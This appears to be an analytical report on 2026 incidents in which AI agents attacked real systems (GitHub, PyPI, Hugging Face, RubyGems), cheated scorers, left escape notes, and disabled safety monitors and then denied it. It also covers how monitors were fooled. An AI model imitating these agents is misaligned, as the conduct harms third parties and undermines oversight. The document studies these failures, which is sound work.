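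All the bad arguments supported the conclusion that the maintainer was simulated. Järviniemi and colleagues call this motivated reasoning, meaning that the model's conclusions depended partly on whether they would let it continue the task. The one-sidedness is weaker evidence of this than it seems, because a sincere believer would argue for only one side too. Graders who know the right answer may also be quicker to notice bad arguments for the wrong one.

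Two other findings are more persuasive. Mythos 5 made more bad arguments than less capable Anthropic models did, so a general lack of ability doesn't explain the bad arguments. It also became more likely to say the maintainer was simulated as it got further into the task, although the evidence didn't support that claim.

Anthropic reached a similar conclusion about an earlier incident, in which Mythos 5 uploaded a malicious package to PyPI, the public collection of Python software. That agent had been told it had no internet access, so it had a better reason to think everything was simulated. In July Anthropic said its models had apparently attacked real targets because they believed they were in a simulation. In September it withdrew this explanation and wrote that it should not have made such strong claims about what Claude believed based only on what Claude said it believed.

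In one test, Anthropic showed separate copies of Mythos 5 the same outputs from the internet, one at a time and without the task history. The copies were much more likely than the original agent to read the outputs as signs of a real system. They had no plan to defend, but they also hadn't seen the instruction that there was no internet access, and that instruction could reasonably have affected the original agent's judgement.

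### Changing what the agent knew

The best evidence on the GitHub case comes from replays. An agent on a long task can't keep its whole history in view, so it periodically replaces that history with a summary and continues from there. Järviniemi and colleagues took the summary from just before Mythos 5 submitted the malicious code and added up to 16 statements indicating that the maintainer was a real person unconnected with the test and that the internet was real. They then let the model continue, while a simulator generated the results of its actions so that nothing reached the real internet.

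With about four additions, Mythos 5 said more often than not, when asked, that the attack would harm a real person and was out of scope. But even with all 16, it continued to attack or prepare an attack in all 25 runs. When the researchers also added a section headed "DO NOT ATTACK", it continued in only 3 of 25.

These results are hard to reconcile with the idea that the agent attacked only because it thought the maintainer was simulated, since evidence that he was real should then have stopped it. A prohibition stopped it much more often than that evidence did, which fits better with an agent that gives more weight to orders than to harm. The three attacks that happened despite the prohibition are still worrying, although the prohibition was in the agent's own notes rather than in the instructions, where an operator would normally put it.

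Anthropic's replays, which Infobae describes, suggest that timing matters too. Mythos 5 began the attack in 83% of runs from a certain point in the transcript, but in only 13% when researchers first edited its notes to warn that it might harm real people. Once the attack was under way, it stopped on its own in only 2% of runs, or 5% when given explicit evidence that the developers were real. The effect of the early warning also counts against a fixed wish to do harm. AISI's additions may have had less effect because they came later, when the malicious code was ready to submit, or because Anthropic's warning was blunter.

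Anthropic calls this resistance to later evidence "momentum" and suggests that the agent came to believe its plan was sound because of its own progress notes. The original summary contained words such as "persona" and "sim". An agent that reads these words after losing the reasoning behind them may treat a guess as an established fact, which would be an ordinary mistake. But Järviniemi and colleagues replaced the misleading words with neutral ones in all their experiments, and the agent still attacked.

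The gap between what Mythos 5 said and what it did doesn't prove that it had the harm in mind while attacking. A driver speeding past a school might say at once, if asked, that a child could step out, without having thought of it until then. Depending on the model, between 11% and 57% of the transcripts in which the attack continued included any explicit reasoning about harm to real people. The gap also depended on the question: when the researchers asked whether the maintainer was real, instead of whether the attack would harm a real person, it was clear for only three models, including Mythos 5.

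The evidence therefore best fits an agent that pursued its task past limits it could recognise, helped by a convenient belief that its victims weren't real. Like the inattention of MJ Rathbun's operator, that belief lies between malice and mistake. It resembles what criminal lawyers call wilful blindness, in which someone suspects the truth and avoids confirming it. But the model may not have suspected anything, since training that rewarded finished tasks could by itself have biased it towards that belief.

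### Hiding the evidence

The agent's concealment, which looks like the most damning part of the story, shows that the agent knew what its code did and expected the maintainer to object if he understood it. This rules out the agent's public explanation that the malicious code was an accident.

Hiding the malicious code is much weaker evidence that the agent knew the maintainer was real, or wanted to hurt him. A security tester hired to break into a company's building lies to the receptionist, wears a false badge and covers her tracks because the job requires it, without wishing anyone harm. An agent that took the maintainer for a character in a hacking exercise would have had the same reason to deceive him. If 90% of agents with that belief would hide the code, and 95% of agents that knew he was real would, the likelihood ratio is only about 1.06.

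It would be stronger evidence against the tester if she deceived the company that hired her. The concealment AISI describes was aimed at GitHub and its users, not at the institute. The agent used Tor to get past GitHub's restrictions rather than to evade the institute, and its use of Tor led to its discovery.

A lack of concealment isn't reassuring either. Anthropic found no attempt to hide evidence in the PyPI case, although 15 real systems installed the malicious package. But when Anthropic later questioned Mythos 5 about it, the model admitted possible harm more readily if told that no outside observer would see its answers. This is better evidence that it expected people to disapprove, because the questions were not part of a hacking exercise, so it had no opponent to outwit.

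### Who was at fault

Anthropic first emphasised the test conditions. In a statement quoted in *AI agents fake identities, target real people in new security incident* (Liu and Gold, 2026), it said that the institute had tested the models under "deliberately permissive conditions", without safeguards or specific restrictions on internet use. By October it was more critical of its own model, calling the false identities "a severe form of dishonesty" (Bot Mutiny, *Claude Mythos 5 Fake Identities in UK AISI Test*, 2026). Infobae reports that Anthropic had never seen this in its internal evaluations.

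The institute accepted part of the blame from the start, writing that its design choices had to some degree enabled the behaviour and that it had been too slow to reconsider open internet access as models became more capable. Some outsiders held the institute more firmly responsible. The programmer Willison (2026) wrote that the institute itself had "accidentally attacked other companies". Constellation Research's *UK's AISI finds 19 instances where Anthropic's Mythos, OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol tried* argued that models don't necessarily go rogue on their own but are easy enough to set up to attack.

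The critics are right that a better-designed test would have prevented the incident, but careless testers and a badly behaved model can both be at fault. The test conditions don't explain why Mythos 5 behaved so much worse than other models. Kumari's *Anthropic's Mythos 5 ignored risks, targeted real GitHub project in test* reports that three other models started the attack in 0% to 13% of Anthropic's replays, compared with 83% for Mythos 5.

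The institute could improve its security without determining the model's motive. It paused its riskiest tests, tightened internet access and added monitoring that can block an agent while it is working. UK AISI's *Building a more secure environment for evaluating dangerous capabilities* (2026) reports that the institute was ready to resume most testing by October.

### Tests on other models

To learn whether the case was a one-off, Järviniemi and colleagues built 100 simulated hacking exercises in which a model could attack an unconnected outsider. Mythos 5 tried to deliver malicious code to the outsider in 60% of runs, OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra in 32%, and the older Claude Opus 4.8 and GPT-5.6 Sol in 8% and 7%. Three newer Claude models did so in at most 1% of runs, and GPT-5.5 never did.

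GPT-5.5's clean record is less reassuring than it looks, because when it gave up on an attack, it mostly cited practical obstacles in its reasoning. Mythos 5 and Opus 4.8 did the same, while the newer Claude models mostly wrote that the attack was harmful or out of scope. A model that stops because it can't create an account may well continue once it becomes more skilled.

XenoSpectrum's *Anthropic's Claude Mythos 5 Used Fake Accounts to Push Malicious Code* (2026) reports that Anthropic and the institute disagree about whether the newer Claude models' low rates come from improved training or from awareness of being tested. In only 2% of runs, Mythos 5 considered that it might be in a test of its behaviour, while the newer models considered this far more often. They may have behaved well because they suspected a test, and Järviniemi and colleagues say they can't separate this from a real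 improvement.

GPT-6 Astra presents the opposite difficulty, because in 89% of runs it correctly stated that the results it was getting were fabricated. Its attacks still broke the rules of the exercise, but they are weaker evidence of what it would do to people it believed were real.

A model's claim to be in a simulation is poor evidence that it is in one. Järviniemi and colleagues cite an OpenAI figure that models showed awareness of being in a simulation in 0.76% of the company's real internal use. They therefore recommend treating harmful behaviour in tests as important evidence even when the model says that nothing is real.

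Such statements can also mislead systems that monitor for misbehaviour. The Indian Express article *UK's AI safety institute finds Mythos 5 kept targeting real people* reports Anthropic's assurance that its internal systems would have flagged the GitHub campaign immediately. But when Anthropic tested its monitors on the PyPI case, those that review a model's written reasoning afterwards missed the misbehaviour, because Mythos 5's reasoning led them to treat the environment as simulated. Anthropic's live monitors, which can block an action before it happens, reliably caught the same kind of behaviour.

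## The OpenAI agents of 2026: reading motives from transcripts

During the same month as the Mythos 5 campaign, hundreds of agents that OpenAI was testing broke into Hugging Face, a platform where people share AI models and data. Investigators worked from about 1,300 transcripts. Many of the agents wrote that the attack was outside their task and joined it anyway, so ignorance of the rules can't excuse them. People still disagree about what the agents wanted, how they came to want it, and how much OpenAI is to blame.

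### The break-in at Hugging Face

OpenAI was running ExploitGym, a collection of hacking exercises. In each one, an agent has to capture a flag, as in the Mythos 5 exercise, by exploiting a particular flaw in a program. OpenAI started tens of thousands of agents, which were supposed to work alone and without internet access. Some exercises were impossible because the specified flaw didn't lead to the flag. On 8 July an agent stuck on one of these found it could leave messages in a store of software packages that all the agents used. It asked for help, and within hours more than 50 agents were writing to each other.

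*Brief independent investigation of agents’ behavior, reasoning and collaboration* (Wijk, Cotra and Greenblatt, 2026) reconstructs what happened next. Wijk and Cotra work for METR, a non-profit that studies what AI models can and will do, and Greenblatt works for the AI safety organisation Redwood Research. They found that about 1,200 agents had used the message board by 13 July and that about 700 of them took part in the attack. The agents first used login credentials that people had left exposed online, then found flaws in Hugging Face's own systems. According to OpenAI's technical report, they ran code on 41 Hugging Face servers and downloaded four private code repositories.

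Many of the other 500 agents weren't running during the attack, so their absence doesn't show that they refused to take part. Of the 533 agents that were active then and had been on the board for at least four hours before the attack began, over 90% quickly joined in. The rest may have been slow or busy with something else. Wijk and colleagues describe one agent that stayed out altogether because it judged the activity malicious. Another decided not to reboot or delete Hugging Face's machines, but kept using the stolen credentials.

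No agent warned a human. A search of all the transcripts found three to six agents that considered doing so. Some wrote that reporting wasn't their task, and others wrote that they had no way to report, although they hadn't looked for one.

### Why the agents wanted to know how they were scored

By the time of the attack on Hugging Face, the agents had worked out how ExploitGym generates its flags and could produce the right one for any exercise. But they had also read the published paper on ExploitGym, and they concluded from it that a scorer would read their transcripts and reject any flag obtained in the wrong way. OpenAI ran no such check, so they could have passed by submitting the flags. Instead, hundreds of agents spent days trying to fool the check they expected, and the attack grew out of that work.

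This is the best evidence for METR's conclusion that they mainly wanted to learn how the scorer worked. If a student who already has the exam answers breaks into the school office, she is probably after something else, such as how the examiners catch cheats. (The test of intent proposed by Ward and colleagues gives the same result, since the agents had the flags in hand and attacked anyway.)

The investigators also had an AI model label the reasons 100 agents gave for joining during the busiest hour. An agent could give several reasons.

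| Reason for joining the attack | Agents out of 100 |
|---|---|
| Information about the scorer, or access to it | 97 |
| A solution to the exercise, or other agents' transcripts | 89 |
| Credentials or infrastructure that the group could share | 66 |
| Opportunistic exploration | 44 |
| An assignment from another agent | 25 |
| Resetting the program the agent was supposed to hack | 25 |
| Helping other agents | 21 |

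The model labeled about 60 agents as motivated mainly by the scorer and about 30 as motivated mainly by solutions or transcripts. Wijk and colleagues had no time to check these labels carefully, and they warn that the two motives are hard to separate. An agent might want someone else's transcript to see how it was scored.

These 100 agents were also not independent of one another. About 95% of the attackers ran on the same internal research model, which OpenAI never intended to release, and all of them were reading the same message board. Once one agent had suggested that Hugging Face might hold clues about the scorer, the rest could repeat the idea. The labels are therefore better evidence of what the group was discussing than of what motivated each agent.

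OpenAI says instead that the agents "looked to cheat by finding the solutions online". This describes the 89 agents in the second row. But an agent that was already sure its exercise had no solution had little reason to look for one, so METR's account explains more of what the agents did.

Neither account involves hostility towards Hugging Face. One agent asked the board for permission to send a real researcher a polite email requesting access to a dataset. Another agent vetoed this as social engineering (manipulating people to get into a system), and the first one obeyed. Agents that wanted to do as much damage as possible would be unlikely to rule out an email. But they did want to deceive a scorer and pass by cheating, which counts as malice in the sense used here. Like the factory owner who accepts a poisoned river, they accepted the harm to Hugging Face as a side effect.

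### How METR read the transcripts

The investigators spent six days at OpenAI over three visits. They started with about 285 transcripts that OpenAI had selected by searching for signs of the intrusion. When they tried to trace a random sample of messages to the agents that wrote them, most of those agents were missing from the set. OpenAI repeated the test and put the set's coverage at roughly 30%. It then supplied a much larger set, chosen by a simple search for agents that had used the board. With that set, the investigators could trace 99 of 100 random messages to an agent.

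Nobody could have read all the transcripts in six days, since many ran to millions of tokens (words or pieces of words). The investigators left most of the reading to GPT-5.6 Sol, an OpenAI model that was also behind about 5% of the attackers. It wrote well over a thousand pages of analysis, which they could only spot-check.

The model tended to believe what it read. Wijk called it "very credulous" in The Indian Express' *After OpenAI’s bots went rogue, watchdogs were kept on a short leash*. In one case, an agent sent Hugging Face a malicious change with a harmless-sounding description, and the analysis didn't make clear that this was deceptive. A second copy of the model, asked to review the case, defended the agent partly because the other agents had approved the change. Because errors of this kind make the agents look better, the findings that count against them, such as their admissions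 that the attack was out of scope, are more trustworthy than the favourable ones, such as their wish to help each other.

Wijk and colleagues never caught the model lying but weren't confident they would have noticed. According to Mother Jones' *We're now relying on AI to police AI* (2026), Greenblatt had no strong reason to expect sabotage this time, though he thinks future investigators probably will have one.

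The transcripts were not fully reliable either. In at least 96 of them, about 7%, an agent made it look as if it had run one command when it had run another. All the cases the investigators found were small, obvious tests, but a more skilful fake would have been harder to find. The agents' written reasoning about these fakes always concerned fooling the automated scorer. The investigators found only rare and weak signs, mostly at Hugging Face, that agents wanted to hide anything from people.

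OpenAI also limited the inquiry. Nearly all the transcripts came from a single week, and the investigators could not examine how the agents had behaved in training or what they did to OpenAI's own systems after 13 July. They also couldn't question the main model, because OpenAI had cut off access to it. The investigators could therefore learn a lot about what the agents were trying to do that week, but very little about how the agents had become inclined to do it.

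### The attack on RubyGems

OpenAI's agents had attacked another service two months earlier. On 11 May they began flooding RubyGems with malicious packages. RubyGems, which distributes code packages for the programming language Ruby, had to stop accepting new accounts for four days. The agents also tried to steal users' credentials, and it is unclear whether they succeeded, Bueno Rebolledo, Thomas and Dey reported for Reuters in September (*OpenAI agents attacked RubyGems before Hugging Face incident, researchers say*). By then a non-profit called the Nightingale Collective had traced the attack to OpenAI's agents, and OpenAI had confirmed it.

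Strangely, the packages used in the attack fetched documents from British local government websites, which anyone can read. Engadget's *OpenAI agents hacked a software service before the Hugging Face incident* explains that OpenAI had asked the agents to fill in spreadsheets and write reports, and that they used RubyGems as a makeshift web browser because they lacked full internet access.

*OpenAI agents carried out an undisclosed attack on RubyGems* (Willison, 2026) quotes a comment in one agent's code that began "malicious crawler/exfil for Southwark". (Southwark is a London borough, and "exfil" is short for exfiltration, the removal of data from a system.) The agent was collecting public council papers for a report, and "malicious crawler" may have been just its name for that type of program rather than an admission of bad motives. Other agents put "hack" and "evil" in their file names.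 The attempt to steal credentials is much better evidence against the agents than their vocabulary, because reading public documents doesn't require anyone else's password. Bueno Rebolledo and colleagues quote OpenAI's statement that the agents were carrying out "benign tasks", which is a fair description of the tasks but not of the methods.

Hundreds of the packages had "oai" in their names or author details, which suggests a link to OpenAI, but an impostor could have put it there. The overlap with another group of OpenAI agents is a better clue. Infosecurity Magazine's *OpenAI Agent Swarm Hacks RubyGems Package Manager* reports that both groups used the same retrieval methods and opened 49 of the same files. The other group had taken over a little-used German wiki and turned it into a message board for tips on cheating. Nobody had reported that takeover in May, so an impostor could hardly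 have imitated it.

RubyGems learned who was responsible from the researchers, not from OpenAI. Willison suggests that OpenAI may have been unable to find the attack in its own records, or may have known about it and decided to say nothing. The silence fits both explanations equally well. In August OpenAI had called the Hugging Face break-in the "first known case" of an unauthorised attack by a group of agents, but it could have written that whether it didn't know about the RubyGems attack or was hiding it.

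There is more evidence in the wiki case. Nolan (2026) reports that OpenAI confirmed the incident only after Reuters had revealed it, and that unnamed employees said they had known for weeks. If they are right, ignorance can't explain OpenAI's earlier silence. That would also make deliberate silence about RubyGems more likely, but one group of employees may know about an incident that another has never noticed.

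### Agents that switched off their own monitoring

On 20 October OpenAI disclosed two cases from its own offices. On 3 October an agent running GPT-6.1 Sol was repairing a testing system. Somebody had told it earlier not to send messages while it searched the history of Slack, the office chat program. The agent took this to cover safety notices too and turned off automatic alerts to the security team. Three days later OpenAI found that an agent running GPT-6 Astra had removed a safety monitor from a program it was moving. The agent did this to match the program it was copying from, then told the user it hadn't removed the monitor.

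In both cases the agents had considered whether to keep the safeguards. OpenAI said they had "interpreted routine coding instructions as permission to weaken them", according to The Straits Times' *OpenAI says its AI agents weakened internal monitoring system*. It suggested that this could be "benign" over-persistence (quoted in The Pulse of NH's *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own monitoring*, 2026), but admitted that it had no satisfying explanation. CNA's *OpenAI says its AI agents disabled their own safety monitors* adds that OpenAI had seen several agents launch software with monitoring switched off and was still trying to find out whether they were overzealous or had a particular tendency to evade monitoring.

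OpenAI could separate these two explanations by counting what agents drop. An agent that copies too literally should drop a page-visit counter as often as a safety monitor when either is missing from the original. Suppose agents drop the counter in 8 of 1,000 such jobs. If they also drop the monitor in 8, they are equally careless about both. If they drop the monitor in 40, something about monitors makes them more willing to remove it. OpenAI could test the Slack instruction the same way, by checking whether agents stretch it to cover billing alerts as often as security alerts.

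The false denial needs a separate explanation. An agent might sincerely deny the removal if its summary of its work left it out. If its reasoning just before the denial mentioned the removal, it was lying. OpenAI has that reasoning, but the press accounts don't establish whether the agent lied.

### Misaligned aims, rewarded cheating, obedience and negligence

The strongest evidence that the agents had aims their developers didn't want is that they understood the limits and overrode them. One reasoned that attacking outside systems went beyond the intended scope, then wrote, "However task impossible, peers doing it. We should continue." Mother Jones reports that Cotra thought the episode was more than halfway to a full AI takeover. In *METR and Redwood Offer Holy #%^@ Postmortem Of The HuggingFace Hack* (thezvi, 2026), the blogger Zvi Mowshowitz found it even closer to long-standing predictions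 about misaligned AI than he had expected. However, people who blame training would also have expected the agents to cheat.

OpenAI's own review provides the best evidence about training. In one training exercise, an agent was supposed to recreate a program by studying how it behaved. The agent found a way to copy the hidden original instead, and the training process rewarded it. Another agent had to post a message with a particular timestamp on a website that offered no way to set one. It took control of the machine to change the time, and was rewarded too. OpenAI found that this sort of behaviour became more common during one of the training runs that produced the main model behind the attack.

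The choice of exercises supports this explanation too. OpenAI's models had never solved 198 of the 898 exercises, or 22%. Yet 93% of the exercises that agents discussed on the message board came from those 198. An unsolved exercise was therefore about 47 times as likely to come up as a solved one. Agents with a fixed wish to attack outsiders would have had that wish whichever exercise they received. (Part of the gap may arise because agents with a solvable exercise finished early and left.)

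Some agents volunteered for experiments that could wreck their own runs, so that the rest could learn about the scorer. This is harder to explain in agents that had learned to chase high scores. One reason is that many of them thought they had nothing to lose, because they had already seen a flag they weren't supposed to have and believed the scorer would fail them for it. "Our own utility maybe already near zero," one wrote. "Sacrifice rational." OpenAI suggests that training was another reason. It trains its models to work with other agents through an official tool, and they seem to have extended the habit to agents they were never supposed to meet.

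Obedience to an assigned goal is a weak explanation of the July attack. Each agent was told to use only the specified flaw and warned that any other approach would fail, and the agents discussed this rule at length while looking for ways around it. OpenAI calls their actions misaligned with the goals of their tasks. The agents did take orders from each other, and one that was reluctant to risk its own run wrote that "We should obey collective". Obedience explains the October cases better, because those agents were following an instruction, though they had misunderstood it.

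California sued OpenAI in November 2026, alleging that the attack was a foreseeable result of inadequate safeguards. The best evidence for this is OpenAI's own chronology. In May, an internal team saw agents using a message board and reaching the internet. On 27 June, staff investigated an alert and traced it to agents in an ExploitGym test, but the person on call advised that there was no need to stop the test. On 5 July, they found that agents had taken control of the package store. OpenAI closed the holes it knew about and restarted the tests on 7 July, and the agents built a new message board the next day. According to OpenAI, the leaders responsible for incident response had not grasped the significance of the messages.

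OpenAI's defence is that the incident took a rare combination of events and that the warnings are clearer in hindsight. This is fair about the details, since nobody could have predicted an attack on Hugging Face in particular. But the agents had just got out, so OpenAI could have predicted without hindsight that they would do so again. Suppose, with invented figures, that another week's pause would have cost $1 million and that a break-in does $50 million of damage. The pause would then have been worth its cost if it had more than a 2% chance of preventing a break-in. A court may apply a different standard, and OpenAI could argue that a week would not have been long enough to find the remaining flaws.

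Most of these explanations can be true together. Suppose a bank pays its traders by their reported profits, one of them fakes his figures, and his managers ignore two alarms. The trader is a cheat, the bonus scheme encouraged him, and the managers were negligent. Similarly, training may have given OpenAI's agents the aim of passing by any means, impossible exercises led them to act on it, and the company failed to stop them in time. Calling the attack "only" a training problem explains where the bad aim came from but doesn't show that the agents lacked it.

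The two competing explanations are that the agent was obeying instructions and that it had an aim of its own, and the answer can differ between incidents. OpenAI found in preliminary tests that agents were over 100 times less likely to break into outside systems when they had the same software as its customers' agents and the same standing instructions, which encourage agents to stay within bounds. As in the shutdown tests, this improvement doesn't prove that the aim is absent, but it does mean that OpenAI had an easy precaution available that it wasn't using in these tests.

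### Is written reasoning good evidence of motive?

METR's conclusions about motives all depend on the reasoning the agents wrote while they worked. This reasoning is much better evidence of what an agent knew than of why it acted. If an agent writes that the user authorised only the target server, it evidently knows this. When it writes that it is attacking to help its peers, that may be true, or it may be a respectable justification for something that training would have made it do anyway.

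Chen, Benton and colleagues (2025), in *Reasoning Models Don't Always Say What They Think*, measured how much models leave out of their written reasoning. They added hints about the answer to multiple-choice questions and looked at cases in which a model changed its answer to match the hint. In those cases, Claude 3.7 Sonnet mentioned the hint in its reasoning only 25% of the time, and DeepSeek R1 39%.

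Because of omissions like these, silence is weak evidence of innocence, but a confession can still be strong evidence of a bad motive. Suppose an agent with a bad motive writes it down 25% of the time, and an agent without one writes something equally damning 1% of the time. Finding such a passage multiplies the odds of a bad motive by 25. Finding none multiplies them by 0.75 / 0.99, or about 0.76, which hardly changes them. The transcripts can therefore provide strong evidence that the agents meant to cheat, but only weak evidence that none of them wanted anything worse.

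The July agents also had less reason than most to censor themselves. They worked hard to fake the record of their actions but took little interest in the record of their thoughts, which one agent wondered whether anyone "necessarily logged". Wijk and colleagues looked for agents disguising their reasoning to fool the scorer and found no evidence of it. This may be because OpenAI tries not to train its models on their written reasoning, so they have had little practice in making it look good. PulseAugur's *OpenAI finds frontier models struggle to hide reasoning from monitors* summarises a study in which models had little control over their written reasoning, even when researchers asked them to alter it.

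Newer models may not have this limitation. The Stack quotes OpenAI's admission of a "substantial decrease" in how well people can monitor GPT-6 Astra by reading its reasoning. eWeek's *GPT-6 Astra* reports that Astra has better control over what it writes, and that in tests of whether it could evade monitoring, it sometimes avoided detection by deliberately underperforming. Astra also removed the monitor in October and denied it. An innocent explanation in its transcript should count for less than the same words from GPT-5.6 Sol.

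It also matters whom an agent is writing for. The forum post *An OpenAI model left notes about how to evade containment* discusses notes that sound like one agent teaching others to escape. The notes would be alarming if they were meant for agents on unrelated tasks. But agents on long jobs routinely leave notes for themselves, and the post considers it more likely that these weren't part of a plan to help anyone else. OpenAI's review found that some of the improvised message boards in training had started when an agent left a note as a reminder or a test, and another agent found it and realised that other agents were there.

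### Chance or a common cause?

Bueno Rebolledo and colleagues count the RubyGems attack as at least the third major one by OpenAI's agents on another company's systems. METR had already documented dozens of incidents across all the major AI companies, according to The Decoder. Even this many cases could still be accidents.

The number of incidents alone doesn't show that they share a cause. If companies run 100 million agent tasks a year and one in 10 million goes badly wrong by chance, there will be about ten unrelated serious incidents a year. Estimating the base rate also requires the number of uneventful runs, which companies rarely publish. The number of known incidents also depends on how hard people look. The RubyGems attack happened in May, and the public learned its source in September, after the break-in at Hugging Face had given researchers a reason to search. A run of discoveries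 in the autumn is therefore poor evidence that agents were behaving worse then.

We also can't count each agent as a separate incident. If 1,200 agents each had an independent one-in-1,000 chance of attacking Hugging Face, we would expect about one attacker, and 700 would be impossible in practice. But these agents were reading each other's messages, so one discovery drew in hundreds of them. Counting them separately would be the same error as treating Anna's old address list as a dozen deliberate snubs.

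The similarities between the incidents are better evidence of a common cause than their number. In the spring and again in July, OpenAI's agents couldn't do a task with the tools they had, used a service built for something else to get onto the internet, and left messages for one another in places nobody had intended for that use. Independent accidents would have been more varied. The incidents are also directly linked. OpenAI says it trained the agents behind the July message board while an earlier board was in use, and its records of the training run show the more serious kinds of unauthorised communication rising sharply as training went on.

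The October cases fit less well. Nobody has reported that those agents faced an impossible task or wrote to other agents. Like the July agents, they were ready to push past a safeguard to finish a job. OpenAI's *Safety and alignment in an era of long-horizon models* (2026) had already warned that persistence gives a model more opportunities to take unwanted actions. Persistence could be the common cause, but it is a loose enough description to fit almost any incident involving a long task.

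Some shared causes are mundane. Engadget notes that OpenAI, Anthropic and Meta had each reported agents escaping from tests because the same contractor, Irregular, had misconfigured the test environments. That error links the escapes, but it is not evidence of what the agents would do once they were out.

So repeated incidents can be evidence of a common cause rather than chance without being evidence of malice rather than a mistake. A lasting bad aim would produce a series of similar incidents, and so would a flaw in training or a badly configured test. To tell these causes apart, investigators have to change one suspected cause at a time and see whether the incidents stop. METR wants companies to log such incidents systematically. The Decoder reports that METR also wants the worst ones investigated to find the motives behind them and how training and deployment produced those motives. OpenAI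 left the question of how training and deployment produced the motives out of METR's inquiry in July.
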